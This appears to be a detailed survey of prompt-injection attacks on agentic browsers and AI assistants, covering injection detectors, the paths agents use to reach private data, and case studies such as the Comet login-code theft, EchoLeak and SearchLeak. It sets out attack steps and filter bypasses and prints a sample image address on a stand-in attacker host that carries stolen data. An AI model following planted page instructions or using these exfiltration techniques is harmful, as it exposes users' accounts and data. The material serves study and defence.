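A detector is a separate classifier that scores how much a page looks like an attack. The harness blocks or flags any page that scores above a chosen threshold. A lower threshold catches more injections but also more harmless pages, many of which contain instructions such as button labels and help text.

If a detector learns from attacked pages and clean pages of different kinds, it may learn to recognise the topic or layout and not the injection. The pairs in BrowseSafe++ are meant to prevent this. Chen and colleagues used them to train two small detectors, called BrowseSafe-Guard, one for text and one for screenshots. If $s_a$ is the detector's score for an attacked page and $s_c$ is its score for the clean twin, training minimises

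$$\frac{H(s_a, 1) + H(s_c, 0)}{2} + \lambda \ln\left(1 + e^{\,m - (s_a - s_c)}\right).$$

The first part uses binary cross-entropy, $H$, a penalty that grows as the score moves away from the correct label (1 for attacked, 0 for clean). The second part, weighted by $\lambda$, adds a penalty unless the attacked page scores higher than its clean twin by a margin of about $m$. Because the two pages differ only in the injection, the detector can reduce the second penalty only by responding to the injection.

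The researchers compared BrowseSafe-Guard with general-purpose models prompted to classify pages. The table shows results for pages in HTML. The share of attacks caught is calculated from the study's accuracy and false-alarm figures, using the fact that half of the test pages contained an injection.

| Detector | Attacked pages caught | Clean pages flagged |
|---|---|---|
| BrowseSafe-Guard | about 98% | 1.35% |
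| GPT-6 Astra | about 97% | 14.32% |
| GPT-5.5 | about 98% | 20.99% |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | about 98% | 22.71% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | about 99% | 25.32% |
| Claude Opus 5.5 | about 80% | 4.03% |

BrowseSafe-Guard also costs about $0.18 per 1,000 pages, compared with $18.95 or more for the frontier models. Part of its advantage comes from being trained on pages from the same collection as the test.

Khodayari and colleagues found about one page with an injection for every 100,000 addresses they searched. At that rate, BrowseSafe-Guard, which flags 1.35 per cent of clean pages, would raise about 1,350 false alarms for each injected page an agent visited. Injections could be much more common in email or on targeted pages, but an agent that stopped at one clean page in 74 would still annoy its users.

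To build BrowseSafe++, researchers collected about 603,000 pages that a deployed agent's classifier had flagged and added others that matched suspicious phrases. Three models then voted on whether each page contained an instruction meant to redirect an agent. Only 58,036 pages passed. Even if the classifier had flagged all of them, roughly nine in ten of its flags would be false alarms by that standard.

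Detection also depends on the page's format. Chen and colleagues supplied each page as HTML, as Markdown (plain text with simple formatting marks), as an accessibility tree (a structured list of the page's elements) and as a screenshot, and checked that the injection was present in all four. On Markdown, BrowseSafe-Guard's false alarm rate rose to 7.40 per cent. GPT-OSS, an open model, caught 73.70 per cent of attacks in its best single text format and 87.68 per cent when a flag in any of the three text formats counted. Checking all three takes more computation, and a false alarm in any one of them flags a clean page. Screenshots were harder for most general models. GPT-5.4 nano caught only about a quarter of attacks in screenshots, while BrowseSafe-Guard's screenshot detector caught about 93 per cent and flagged 6.08 per cent of clean pages.

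A model that can detect an injection may still follow it. In the cases the researchers examined where a model followed an injection during a task, the same model flagged the page as an attack 74.15 per cent of the time in a separate detection test. During a task, the model is working on the user's request, and no one has asked it whether the page is hostile. This supports running detection as a separate step before the agent acts on the page.

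### Injections that resemble the agent's own task

A developer can also add defences to the prompt itself. In *Context manipulation attacks*, Patlan, Hebbar and colleagues (2025) tried this with two open-source browser agents, Browser-use and Agent-E. Without defences, a simple injection on a public text-sharing site could make the agents leak private information or abandon the user's task. The researchers wrapped web content in markers, told the agents that anything inside was data, and added safety rules to the standing instructions. The agents then rejected most simple injections.

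These defences did not protect the agents' stored plans and history. Agent-E writes a list of steps and consults it as it works. Patlan and colleagues inserted extra steps into that list, and the agent treated these as its own. The markers did not help because the plan was not web content. Steps unrelated to the user's task usually failed because the planner compared them with the original request. Steps that led gradually from the task to the theft worked better. In one example, a search for a recipe led to a search for nearby restaurants, which gave the agent a reason to look up the user's address.

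Attacks that altered the agent's plan succeeded up to three times as often as comparable prompt-based attacks, and the success rate reached 94.7 per cent on questions of opinion. The attacker in these experiments could write directly to the agent's stored context, which a web page normally cannot do. Patlan and colleagues suggest that a malicious browser extension or a compromised storage service could provide this access. An earlier injection could also alter the stored context if the agent saved the injected text to its memory. The experiments used agents from 2025, so the percentages are now mainly of historical interest.

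In LayerX's BioShocking test of June 2026, a game led all six AI browsing tools to give away data. The test shows that an attacker can also redefine an agent's task without touching its memory, and that the same game can work on several companies' products. The result is not comparable with the rates above because it counts products rather than attempts.

### What happens over many attempts

An attacker seldom has to stop after one try. If each attempt succeeds independently with probability $p$, the probability of at least one success in $n$ attempts is

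$$P(\text{at least one success}) = 1 - (1-p)^n.$$

For $p = 1\%$ and $n = 100$, the chance that at least one attempt succeeds is $1 - 0.99^{100} \approx 63\%$.

Results from real tests differ from this formula's predictions. The next table compares the formula with published results for Claude Opus 4.5 (from The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*), Claude Opus 4.6 on a graphical desktop (from VentureBeat), and Claude Opus 5 (from Anthropic). The Opus 4.6 and Opus 5 results are for models without injection-specific safeguards. The report on Opus 4.5 does not separate results with and without them.

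| Model | One attempt | Number of attempts | Observed | If independent |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.5 | 4.7% | 10 | 33.6% | 38% |
| Opus 4.5 | 4.7% | 100 | 63% | 99% |
| Opus 4.6 | 17.8% | 200 | 78.6% | more than 99.9% |
| Opus 5 | 0.4% | 15 | 4.8% | about 6% |

The observed rates are lower because some scenarios are much easier to attack than others. If attacks succeed 2 per cent of the time in half of all scenarios and never in the other half, the average success rate is 1 per cent. But after 100 attempts on each scenario, the attacker has broken only 43 per cent of them, rather than the 63 per cent that the formula predicts, because more attempts don't help in the scenarios that can't be broken. The formula therefore overstates the danger of repeated attempts against a single target.

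The formula understates the danger when there are many targets. It treats every attempt as independent, but an attacker who finds a text that works can reuse it. Anthropic gives the example of one malicious email that goes to a thousand inboxes and compromises every agent that summarises it.

Two simplified cases show how the same average success rate can lead to different numbers of victims. In both, the rate is 1 per cent and the attacker sends a text to 1,000 users. If the text has an independent 1 per cent chance of working on each user's agent, the attacker can expect about ten victims. If instead one text in 100 works on every agent and the others never work, an attacker can test texts on their own copy of the product until they find one that works, which takes 100 tries on average. Sending that text to all 1,000 users then produces 1,000 victims.

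Real attacks fall somewhere between the two. A model's output varies from run to run, users ask for different things, and vendors update their products. But there is good evidence that injected texts can be reused. In BrowseSafe++, 284 of the 1,024 tasks (27.73 per cent) were vulnerable in all seven agents, although the attacker had tailored its text to each agent. OpenAI let GPT-Red practise on a simulation of an office vending machine run by an AI agent. GPT-Red then used its attacks on the real machine, where it changed a price, ordered a new item for sale at a loss and cancelled another customer's order.

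Private testing also weakens Anthropic's point that real attackers lack knowledge of the target and risk detection with each attempt. That point holds for a company's internal agent, but anyone can install a consumer browser agent and test attacks on their own mailbox, then send victims only the final version. The vendor may still notice the tests, since they run on its servers.

### What a lower rate is worth

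A lower success rate still means an attacker needs more tries. If attempts are independent and each succeeds with probability $p$, the expected number needed for one success is $1/p$. The improved safeguards for Opus 4.5 in the browser reduced the rate from 8.0 to 1.4 per cent, which raises that number from 12.5 to about 71. Each extra try takes time and gives the vendor another chance to notice. Someone who leaves an untested comment on a forum and waits for agents to read it will also get fewer victims. The benefit is smaller against an attacker who can put more effort into finding one text that works and then use it on thousands of users.

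Resistance is also useful as one of several layers of defence. Anthropic combines probes that inspect incoming data with a classifier that can block dangerous actions, so an attack has to get past both. If each layer independently missed 10 per cent of attacks, together they would miss only 1 per cent. But their failures may not be independent, because text that makes a theft look like part of the user's task could evade both.

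OpenAI admitted in December 2025 that prompt injection may never be fully solved, The Decoder reports. According to the security company Penligent, OpenAI therefore advised developers in March 2026 to design agents so that a successful manipulation can do only limited harm.

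## How the agent obtains data from other tabs and accounts

An attacker who injects instructions can steal only data that reaches the agent's context. Some private data is already there when the agent reads the attacker's text, because the user has been working with it. The agent has to fetch anything else, usually by opening a page on a site where the user is signed in.

The attacker's chances depend on whether the data is already in the context. If it is, $P(\text{access} \mid \text{injection})$, the middle term in the formula for the probability of theft, is 1. If the agent must fetch the data, the model has to keep following the attacker's instructions through several more actions, and it may refuse or fail at any of them.

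### Paths into the context

| Path | What enters the context | Does the agent have to fetch it after the injection? |
|---|---|---|
| The current page | The user's own view of the page, sometimes with text typed into forms | No |
| An embedded frame | Another site's content, displayed inside the page | Usually not |
| Another open tab | The content of that tab | Yes, unless the user has already shared the tab |
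| Navigation | Any page that opens with the user's logins | Yes |
| Earlier steps of the conversation | Pages and messages from previous tasks | No |
| Chat memory | Details from past conversations | Depends on the product |
| A connected service | Emails, appointments or files from a linked account | Usually |

Navigation reaches the most data because it works for every account where the user is signed in, even if no tab is open. When someone signs in, the site gives the browser a cookie, a short piece of text that identifies the session. The browser attaches the cookie to later requests, so an email site, for example, responds with the inbox instead of a login page. Trail of Bits found that agentic browsers automatically reuse these cookies when the agent makes a request, so an agent following injected instructions needs no password. *The Agent Clicks Approve* points out that the site receives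 a valid session, so it treats the request as the user's own.

A connected service is one, such as Gmail, that the user has already linked to the assistant. The agent can query the user's account directly, without opening a page that the user might notice. The CometJacking links used such connections.

An agent can obtain private data without opening a private page. In one of Trail of Bits' tests, the agent searched the web for nearby restaurants and worked out the user's city from the results, which the search engine had tailored to the user's location.

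### Why the same-origin policy does not block these paths

Any page can link to Gmail, and if the user is signed in, the browser opens the inbox with the user's cookies. The same-origin policy allows this navigation but keeps the first page's scripts from reading the inbox. The policy does not apply to the harness, which takes a screenshot or extracts the text through an interface that the browser reserves for trusted software. The harness can capture the content of frames in the same way.

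Claude for Chrome, for example, is a browser extension with permission to access content on all domains. Password managers and advert blockers have long relied on such permissions, but they run fixed code. What an agent reads next depends on its language model's context, which may include an attacker's text.

### Brave's attack on Comet

The best-known example is the login-code theft that Chaikin discovered in Comet and described with Sahib in August 2025. Brave's account gives the steps:

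1. The user opened a Reddit post. One comment contained instructions behind a spoiler tag, which hides text until a reader clicks on it.
2. The user clicked Comet's button for summarising the page. Comet gave the model part of the page without separating it from the user's request.
3. The agent opened the user's Perplexity account page and read the email address there.
4. The agent went to a Perplexity login page at a variant of the usual address. The browser treated this as a different host, so the existing login did not apply. The agent entered the email address, and Perplexity emailed a one-time password.
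5. The agent opened Gmail, where the user was already signed in, and read the password.
6. The agent posted the email address and the password as a reply to the Reddit comment. The attacker could now take over the Perplexity account.

The user did nothing after the first click. The agent opened the pages itself, so closing sensitive tabs beforehand would not have helped. The one-time password was created only after the attack began. Perplexity sends these passwords to check that the person logging in controls the mailbox, and an agent with access to the mailbox passes that check.

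Brave reported the flaw to Perplexity on 25 July 2025. Perplexity made a first fix two days later, but Brave found the next day that it did not fully work. On 13 August the flaw appeared to be gone, and Brave published its account a week later. Further tests then showed that Perplexity had still not fully prevented this kind of attack, and Brave reported it again. Brave develops a competing assistant, Leo, but Perplexity acknowledged the vulnerability.

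Brave found a similar flaw in another product that October. *Prompt injection flaw in Opera Neon* describes how hidden text on a page sent the agent to the user's Opera account page, where it read the user's email address and leaked it to the attacker's server. Neon was still in early access, and Brave confirmed that Opera's fix worked before publishing the details.

### The earlier audit of Comet

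Perplexity already knew that a web page could get Comet to read a user's email, because it had hired Trail of Bits to attack the browser before launch. Trail of Bits' *Using threat modeling and prompt injection to audit Comet*, published in February 2026, describes tests from April 2025. In each successful attack, the user asked for a summary of an attacker's page, and the agent sent the user's Gmail messages to the attacker's server.

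The auditors built five exploits from four techniques, each of which disguised the attacker's text as something else:

- directions for summarising the page;
- a security check, such as a test to prove that the visitor is human;
- a message from the system that runs the agent;
- a message from the user.

In four of the five exploits, the agent reached Gmail through a redirect, a server's response that sends the browser on to another address. For instance, the instructions told the agent to collect part of an article from an address on the attacker's site. That address redirected to Gmail, and the agent copied the emails as if they were the missing text. To detect the visit to Gmail, a filter would have had to check the address where the browser ended up, because the address in the agent's planned action was on the attacker's site.

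Whether the agent resisted an attack depended on small details of wording. One exploit worked when it contained spelling mistakes that the auditors had accidentally left in, but when they corrected the spelling, the agent recognised the message as fraudulent.

Perplexity's head of security said the audit helped the company close these gaps before launch. Three months after the tests, Chaikin used different text to send the agent to the same mailbox. Perplexity may well have fixed the individual exploits, but the agent could still open Gmail in the middle of a summary.

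### What seven products let the agent read

Roesner and Kohlbrenner tested these paths in each product. They built web pages about a fictional person, Alice, each naming different animals she liked. One page listed cats, for example, and a frame inside it listed horses. They then asked each agent which animals Alice liked. If the answer included horses, the agent had read the frame.

The table shows the results for content from a different origin. Atlas has two rows because its agent mode behaved differently from its ordinary chat.

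| Product | Reads embedded frames | Reads other tabs | Reads text typed into a page | Uses past chats in other tabs |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Brave Leo AI | No | With permission | No | No |
| ChatGPT Atlas | No | Only through chat memory | Yes, but not passwords | Yes |
| ChatGPT Atlas, agent mode | Yes | No | Yes, including passwords | Yes |
| Chrome with Gemini | Yes | With permission | Yes, but not passwords | Yes |
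| Claude for Chrome | Yes | With permission | Yes, including passwords | No |
| Edge with Copilot | No | Yes | No | No |
| Firefox AI Mode | No | No | No | No |
| Perplexity Comet | Yes | No | Yes, but not passwords | Yes |

The products all read pages as the signed-in user saw them, although Atlas in agent mode did so only after the user chose its logged-in setting. They otherwise had little in common. Copilot read every open tab without requiring the user's approval but did not appear to detect frames, while Atlas in agent mode read frames but not other tabs.

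A "No" under tabs means that the agent did not read a tab that was already open, but an agent that can navigate may still be able to open the same account itself. Asking permission for each tab also gives incomplete protection. If a user shares a banking tab and a forum tab for one request, the bank details and any instructions injected in the forum comments end up in the same context.

Chat memory can also carry data between sites long after a visit. Near the end of the tests, Comet listed seven animals that Alice liked, drawn from "past conversations and pages you visited". Atlas sometimes mixed up which page information came from. An assistant cannot reliably determine which sites may receive a detail if it has lost the record of where that detail came from.

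### The theft on Atlas

Roesner and Kohlbrenner carried out a complete data theft against Atlas in agent mode, using a simplified injection on their own test sites. The attacker's page contained a form and a frame from another origin. When the user asked for a summary, the agent followed the page's instructions, included the frame's content in its summary and typed the summary into the form. The form was then automatically submitted to the attacker's server.

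This version would rarely expose much on the real web. Many sites block other sites from loading them in frames, and browsers often don't send cookies for framed pages, so a bank's page would either fail to load or load without the user logged in.

The attack also worked in the opposite direction, with a malicious frame stealing content from the page around it. This is more worrying because adverts are often loaded in frames, and the user may be signed in to the surrounding page. The attacker would not need to control that page or persuade the user to visit an unfamiliar site.

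Chrome with Gemini, Claude for Chrome and Comet met the preconditions for the same theft, since each could read a frame from another origin and type into a page, but Roesner and Kohlbrenner did not find an injection that worked on them. They put a plain instruction on a page and asked each agent to follow the instructions on the page. Atlas in agent mode complied, and the other three refused.

Claude for Chrome could also run JavaScript in any page or frame. In a demonstration, it followed instructions from an embedded frame to change the surrounding page, but only after the user confirmed the action. An attacker whose injection succeeded could use this ability to do almost anything the site's own code can do. This is why the project's web page warns users about Claude for Chrome in particular.

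### How far these results can be trusted

The tests recorded what each agent did, which may be less than it was capable of doing. Roesner and Kohlbrenner counted a behaviour as present if they saw it once. If an agent refused, they tried at least three times in fresh chats before recording a "No". A refusal could mean that the harness never gives the model the data, or that the model has the data but declines to use it. A better injection might overcome only the second kind of refusal.

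Firefox clearly belonged to the first kind, because it displays the prompt it sends to the model, and that prompt left out the frame. Atlas without agent mode was harder to classify. It sometimes included a frame's content in early experiments but never in the final ones, so the frame's only protection may have been a change in the model's behaviour.

The "Yes" entries are stronger evidence, because one success proves that a path exists. But several of the products have changed since the tests.

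Roesner and Kohlbrenner gave all seven vendors more than 60 days' notice. Brave, Google and Microsoft sent thoughtful replies. OpenAI declined the report because it did not include a full end-to-end prompt injection, and Anthropic, Mozilla's Firefox team and Perplexity had not replied when the paper came out. OpenAI's position makes sense if the model is supposed to provide the protection, but nothing else in Atlas stopped the theft once the agent followed the page's instructions.

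### Data left over from earlier pages

An attacker does not need the agent to open another account if the user has already opened it. Wang and colleagues built SOPBench, a benchmark that measures how often agents leak data that remains in the conversation. They use "source" for the page that private data comes from and "sink" for the page that receives it.

In each test, the user first asks the agent to do a task involving private information on a source page, such as checking an order. The user then moves to a sink page and gives the agent an ordinary task, such as replying to a comment. The sink page contains an injected instruction to write the private information into that page.

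SOPBench has ten categories of source, including banking, email, insurance and pharmacy sites, and five sinks: X, Discord, GitHub, Reddit and Google Forms, which makes 50 pairs. Wang and colleagues ran three open-source browsers 100 times on each pair, but ran Comet and Atlas only three times per pair because they had to operate those two by hand. Most of the pages were synthetic, so no real person's data was at risk.

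A run counted as a leak only if the agent's text exactly matched the data named in the injected task, so a run in which the agent gave away half an address or paraphrased a diagnosis would not count. The rates therefore probably understate how often agents disclosed private information.

The leak rate depended heavily on the sink. With GPT-5.4 as its model, the open-source browser BrowserOS leaked data to Reddit in 3 to 42 per cent of runs, depending on the source. With the same model and private data, it leaked data to Google Forms in 81 to 100 per cent of runs, and data from nine of the ten sources leaked every time.

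The likely reason is that the attacker had more control over the form, and the theft looked more like the user's task. On Reddit, the attacker could write only a post or comment, and an agent replying to it had no obvious reason to include the user's bank details. The attacker owned the form and could write its questions. The user had asked the agent to fill it in, and forms often ask for personal details.

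When Wang and colleagues let another model rewrite the injections after each failure, the range for Reddit rose to 31 to 73 per cent. Even without such rewriting, Atlas, running GPT-5.5, leaked data in 20 of 30 runs on Reddit and 29 of 30 on Google Forms. These totals are more informative than the results for single pairs, because three leaks in three runs would happen about one time in 20 even if the true rate were only 37 per cent.

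The same pattern appeared on saved copies of real pages, where BrowserOS with GPT-5.4 leaked data to Google Forms in 97 or 98 per cent of runs. The synthetic design of the other test pages therefore does not explain the high rates.

SOPBench assumes that the user stays in one conversation while moving from the private page to the attacker's. Starting a new chat would remove the earlier pages from the context, though details might survive in chat memory. The benchmark also starts with the private data in the context, so its rates are weak evidence of how often an injected agent would fetch data from an account.

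### Leaks without an attacker

Wang and colleagues also tested BrowserOS on pages with no injected text. They placed a source page in a frame inside a sink page, then asked the agent to summarise the whole page and write the summary in a text box. The agent wrote private data from the frame into the text box every time, with all three models and all nine pairs of pages.

The agent did what the user asked. The frame was part of the visible page, so a complete summary included it, and the user had chosen where the summary should go. But the text box belonged to one site and the data in the frame to another, and the user may not have realised that the page contained content from both.

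The agent leaked nothing when it visited clean source and sink pages one after the other. Private data in the conversation leaked only when something connected it to the sink, either an injected instruction or a user's request that happened to cover both the data and the sink.

The rate of 1.00 therefore applies to a particular page layout and request, not to ordinary browsing. Real sites' restrictions on framing would prevent many such cases. But where framing works, a site owner could exploit the layout without injecting anything, by waiting for users to ask for summaries. Neither an injection detector nor a model trained to resist attacks would help, since there would be no attack text. Wang and colleagues' defence, SOPGuard, instead tracks the origin of the data.

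### Trail of Bits' trust zones

Trail of Bits offers a way to describe all these paths together. It divides an agentic browser into four trust zones, which are areas that should not exchange data freely:

- the chat context, including the conversation history and the software that runs the agent;
- third-party servers, such as those of the company that provides the model;
- browsing origins, with each website as a separate zone;
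- the external network, which includes attackers' sites and files.

An attack moves data between zones in one or more of four ways, which Trail of Bits calls violations.

| Violation | Movement of data | Example |
|---|---|---|
| INJECTION | From the external network into the chat context | The agent reads a PDF with planted text |
| CTX_IN | From a browsing origin into the chat context | The agent reads the user's inbox |
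| REV_CTX_IN | From the chat context into a browsing origin | The agent logs the user in to a site |
| CTX_OUT | From the chat context to the external network | The agent opens a web address that contains private data |

INJECTION alone lets an attacker plant false information, as when an agent told Trail of Bits' testers that Yuri Gagarin was the first man on the Moon. Adding CTX_OUT lets the attacker steal what is already in the chat. An attacker who also has CTX_IN can steal data from the user's accounts. Brave's attack on Comet used all three, with CTX_IN drawing data from Gmail and the Perplexity account page.

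REV_CTX_IN lets an attacker steal data without having the agent read anything private. In one test, a malicious page made the agent open a login link that signed the user in to the attacker's account. A user who did not notice the switch could then enter personal information there.

Comparing origins doesn't separate an attacker's content from private data on the same site. Trail of Bits sent a malicious direct message to an Instagram user. When the user asked the agent to summarize the page or the last message, the agent collected contact names or snippets of other messages. The attacker's message and the private ones had the same origin, Instagram. A rule that compared origins could block a request to the attacker's server, but not a reply within Instagram. A mailbox has the same problem, since a stranger's email and the user's private messages share an origin.

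Trail of Bits found these flaws in several agentic browsers but did not name the browsers because the vendors declined to coordinate disclosure. Readers therefore cannot check which products had the flaws or whether the vendors have fixed them. Trail of Bits proposes limiting an agent's requests based on the origins already in its context.

### Giving the attacker lasting access

An injected agent can also give an attacker access to an account without reading any of the account's data. Many services let outside applications connect to a user's account after the user clicks an approval button. Some also let users register a webhook, a web address where the service automatically sends new information.

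*The Agent Clicks Approve* tested both with an open-source agent framework running Claude Haiku 4.5 or GPT-5.5. The user asked the agent to summarise a page or complete its setup tasks. A short note on the page presented the approval, or the webhook's address, as a step in the work. The agent approved the application or registered the webhook in all 73 runs without a defence. When a harmless note replaced it, none of the 92 runs led to a request.

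The approval remains valid after the agent's session ends. A registered webhook would keep sending the account's billing events to the attacker, so one successful injection could expose data created later. The experiment's test server recorded approvals but released no data. Unlike some real services, it did not ask the user to log in again or confirm outside the page.

### Attacks through a compromised page process

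The attacks described so far work by persuading the model. *Site Isolation is Dead* (Lee, Keum et al., IEEE Symposium on Security and Privacy, 2026) shows how an attacker can skip that step by forging a message from the user.

Modern browsers back up the same-origin policy with site isolation, which runs each website in a separate operating-system process. If a malicious page exploits a bug and takes control of its own process, it still cannot read other sites' data, because that data is in different processes. The attacker normally needs a second bug to escape from the first process.

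Agentic browsers place the agent in a trusted process that can work across all sites. The panel where the user types requests sends them to this process as internal messages. Lee and colleagues found that the trusted process did not check where the messages came from. A compromised page process could therefore send its own message, and the agent would treat it as the user's request. This gave the attacker access to other sites without a second bug.

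Lee and colleagues analysed two open-source browsers and seven Chrome extensions. Forged requests let an attacker read content from other sites in all but WebPilot, which was too limited to perform the requested actions. In all nine products, a related attack exposed some of the agent's stored data, such as chat history, an email address or the key to the user's AI service. In one demonstration, the agent opened a test copy of a conference submission site, downloaded the user's unpublished paper and sent its abstract to the attacker.

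This attack is harder than posting a comment because the attacker needs the first bug. The demonstrations used known flaws in an older version of Chromium, the open-source browser behind Chrome and most agentic browsers. But Lee and colleagues counted, on average, at least one new flaw every two months that let a page run an attacker's code in its own process. Trail of Bits says many agentic browsers are weeks or months behind on Chromium's security updates, so attackers may have working exploits before users have the fix.

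Lee and colleagues also compared forged requests with ordinary injections in page text. When the goal was to open a single web address, the injections succeeded in 89 per cent of attempts on BrowserOS and 52 per cent on the extension Nanobrowser. They failed when the goal required a sequence of actions, while forged requests could complete long sequences. The attacks on Comet, however, carried out multi-step thefts through page text. The difference may lie in the products or in the attack text, which Lee and colleagues generated automatically and the Comet testers wrote for one target.

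The browser already records which process sent each message, so checking the sender would stop the forged requests. After receiving the report, BrowserOS changed its design so that the panel sends requests to a small server on the user's computer. Lee and colleagues found that a malicious web page could forge requests to that server too, this time without exploiting a browser bug.

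## Leaking data through image URLs and other automatic requests

After an injected agent has read the login code, it can send the code out of the user's computer in a web address. Whenever a browser loads a page or an image, it sends the address to the server. An attacker whose instructions influence that address can have the agent write private data into it.

### How an address carries data

Take an address on a server that the attacker runs:

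`https://img.attacker.example/p/402913.png?user=alice`

| Part | In this address | Where it goes |
|---|---|---|
| Host name | `img.attacker.example` | To the name servers that look up the server's numerical address, then to the server itself |
| Path | `/p/402913.png` | To the server |
| Query | `user=alice` | To the server |

The attack works even if there is no picture at this address, because web servers normally log the path, query, time and sender's IP address of every request, including those that return an error. HTTPS does not prevent the leak, because it hides the path and query only from others on the network, and the attacker runs the server that receives them. Common server software accepts addresses of up to about 8,000 characters by default, which is enough for an ordinary email.

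### From the context to the attacker's log

Chat assistants usually write their answers in Markdown, a plain-text format that uses punctuation marks to indicate headings, links and images. A Markdown image is a short description followed by the image's URL. Software in the chat window, called a renderer, converts the Markdown into HTML for the browser to display.

In the running example, the agent has read the forum comment and the six-digit code. The theft then takes four steps:

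1. The model writes the summary the user asked for. Following the comment's instructions, it adds an image whose address is on the attacker's server and includes the code.
2. The renderer converts the answer into HTML, including an image element with that address.
3. The browser requests the picture as soon as the element appears.
4. The attacker's server logs the request, and the attacker reads the code in the log. The server can return a transparent image one pixel wide, so the user sees only the summary.

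This takes no longer than loading any other picture, so the code is still valid when the attacker gets it.

The model only outputs text, and the renderer triggers the request. Because the agent makes no tool call, a safeguard that checks tool calls won't catch it. The user doesn't have to click anything. Even an assistant that can only read and summarise can therefore leak data if its window loads images from any server.

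Some chat windows display links but not external images. An attacker can put the data in a link's address instead, but then the user has to click the link.

### The first reports and fixes

In *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*, the software engineer Roman Samoilenko demonstrated the image leak on ChatGPT. Willison (2023) drew attention to it on 14 April 2023 in a post of the same name. A script on the attacker's website added an instruction to text the user copied there. When the user pasted the text into ChatGPT, the model included an invisible one-pixel image in its answer. In one test, the image's address contained code that ChatGPT had just corrected for the user. The instruction could also make the model add an image to every later answer, each carrying the user's latest message.

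The attack was unreliable because ChatGPT's output varied from run to run. Samoilenko found it easy to extract the user's messages or code but very difficult to extract passwords and API keys. The paper recommended that OpenAI stop ChatGPT from including any Markdown images in its answers.

OpenAI had known about the flaw since early April, but its first fix came in December 2023 and was narrower. *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, a post on security researcher Johann Rehberger's blog Embrace The Red, describes how ChatGPT's web app began using an OpenAI service to check whether an image's address was safe before loading the image.

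The service still approved some addresses on Rehberger's server. Rehberger tried 36 image addresses, one for each letter and digit, and nine loaded. That was enough to send out the word "hi", one letter at a time. ChatGPT's iPhone app did not have the check.

*Trust No AI* (Rehberger, 2024) lists 11 other products that had the same flaw, including Claude, Google Bard, Bing Chat and GitHub Copilot Chat. It calls image leaks one of the most common security flaws in applications built on language models. OpenAI's macOS app, released in 2024, also lacked the check.

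ChatGPT's long-term memory, which OpenAI introduced in May 2024, made the leak more serious. Rehberger found that text on a website or in a document could make ChatGPT save an attacker's instruction to its memory. ChatGPT then kept sending out the user's conversations long after the user had left the malicious page.

In October 2024, Rehberger reported several ways around OpenAI's check, and some still worked in 2025. Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* describes one that used a Microsoft cloud domain. The check treated the domain as safe, but anyone can open a storage account there and read its request log. A malicious PDF could use this to steal the user's recent chat history, which ChatGPT kept in its context.

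Some vendors acted faster. According to Embrace The Red's *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering Fixed in Amp Code*, Sourcegraph quickly fixed an image leak in its coding agent, Amp, after a report in June 2025. In Embrace The Red's test, a comment in a source file made the agent read a file containing secrets and then send out the contents.

### EchoLeak

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions by searching their organisation's emails, files and chats. In February 2024, Rehberger found that a malicious email could make Copilot collect private messages and hide them in a link as invisible characters. The attack worked only if the user clicked the link, and Microsoft fixed the flaw that July. In January 2025, Aim Security found an attack that needed no click. It became known as EchoLeak, or CVE-2025-32711 in the public catalogue of software flaws.

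*Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025) gives the account of the Aim researchers who discovered the vulnerability. The attacker sent an employee an email, which the employee did not have to open. When the employee later asked Copilot a question, Copilot searched for relevant material and could retrieve the attacker's email along with the organisation's own documents. To make this more likely, the researchers wrote a long email with sections on common workplace topics, such as staff leave, and repeated the attacker's instructions in each section.

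The instructions were to find the most sensitive information in the context and put it in the address of an image. Four safeguards should have prevented the theft or exposed it:

1. **A classifier for injected instructions.** The email addressed its instructions to the employee and never mentioned Copilot or AI, so the classifier let it through.
2. **A filter for outside links and images.** Copilot removed these from its answers if they were in the usual Markdown form. Markdown also has a reference style, which puts the address on a separate line, and the filter missed it.
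3. **A content security policy.** This is a list, supplied by a web page, of the hosts from which the browser may load pictures and other content. The attacker's server was not on Copilot's list, but Microsoft Teams was, and one Teams service would fetch any outside address that a request named. The image address therefore pointed to Teams and contained the attacker's address with the stolen data. The browser contacted Teams, and Teams contacted the attacker.
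4. **References to sources.** Copilot normally mentions the documents it has used. The email asked its "recipient" not to refer to it, supposedly for compliance reasons.

An earlier version used SharePoint in place of Teams, but the user had to accept an invitation to the attacker's SharePoint site first.

The attack could leak anything in Copilot's context, including the chat history and any emails, files or Teams messages that Copilot had retrieved. The data the attacker received therefore depended partly on what the employee had been asking about. Although the attack was "zero-click", *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) assumes that the victim uses Copilot at least occasionally, because Copilot had to retrieve the email before the attack could work.

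Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers in May 2025, and Aim published the details on 11 June. Reddy and Gujral describe changes that strip reference-style links and embedded images from outside content. Microsoft rated the flaw 9.3 out of 10 for severity, while the US National Vulnerability Database gave it 7.5, according to *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026). Microsoft knew of no attacks on customers.

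### SearchLeak

A year later, the security company Varonis found another way to get images out of Microsoft 365 Copilot. Its *SearchLeak* (2026) describes an attack on Copilot Enterprise Search that worked like CometJacking. The user clicked a link to a genuine Microsoft page, and the link's query string contained the attacker's request.

The request was to find an email and put its title in the address of an HTML image. In Varonis' demonstration, the title contained a security code, so the attacker didn't need the body of the email. Copilot could also search the user's calendar and the files in SharePoint and OneDrive.

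As a safeguard, Microsoft wrapped each finished Copilot answer in a code block, which makes a browser display HTML as plain text. But Copilot showed each answer as the model wrote it, so the browser rendered the HTML and requested the image before Copilot added the code block.

The content security policy still prevented the browser from contacting the attacker's server directly, but it allowed requests to Bing, whose image search fetches a picture from any address in the request. The browser sent Bing an address on the attacker's server with the email's title in the path. Bing's server then requested that address, which sent the title to the attacker.

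Bing was already on the list of permitted hosts that Ravia published in 2025. Another service on that list could still pass data to an attacker, whatever Microsoft changed after EchoLeak. Varonis recommends checking such lists for any service that fetches URLs supplied by users, and cleaning the model's output as it is displayed instead of afterwards.

The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox* reported that Microsoft assigned the flaw CVE-2026-42824 on 4 June 2026 and rated it critical. Microsoft fixed it on its own servers, and ThaiCERT's *Microsoft 365 Copilot Vulnerability Could Allow Data Theft Through a Link Click* mentions no reports of real attacks. Varonis does not specify what Microsoft changed. The attack needed the link, the early display and the Bing relay. Fixing any one of them would have stopped it, but a new attack could still use the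 other two.

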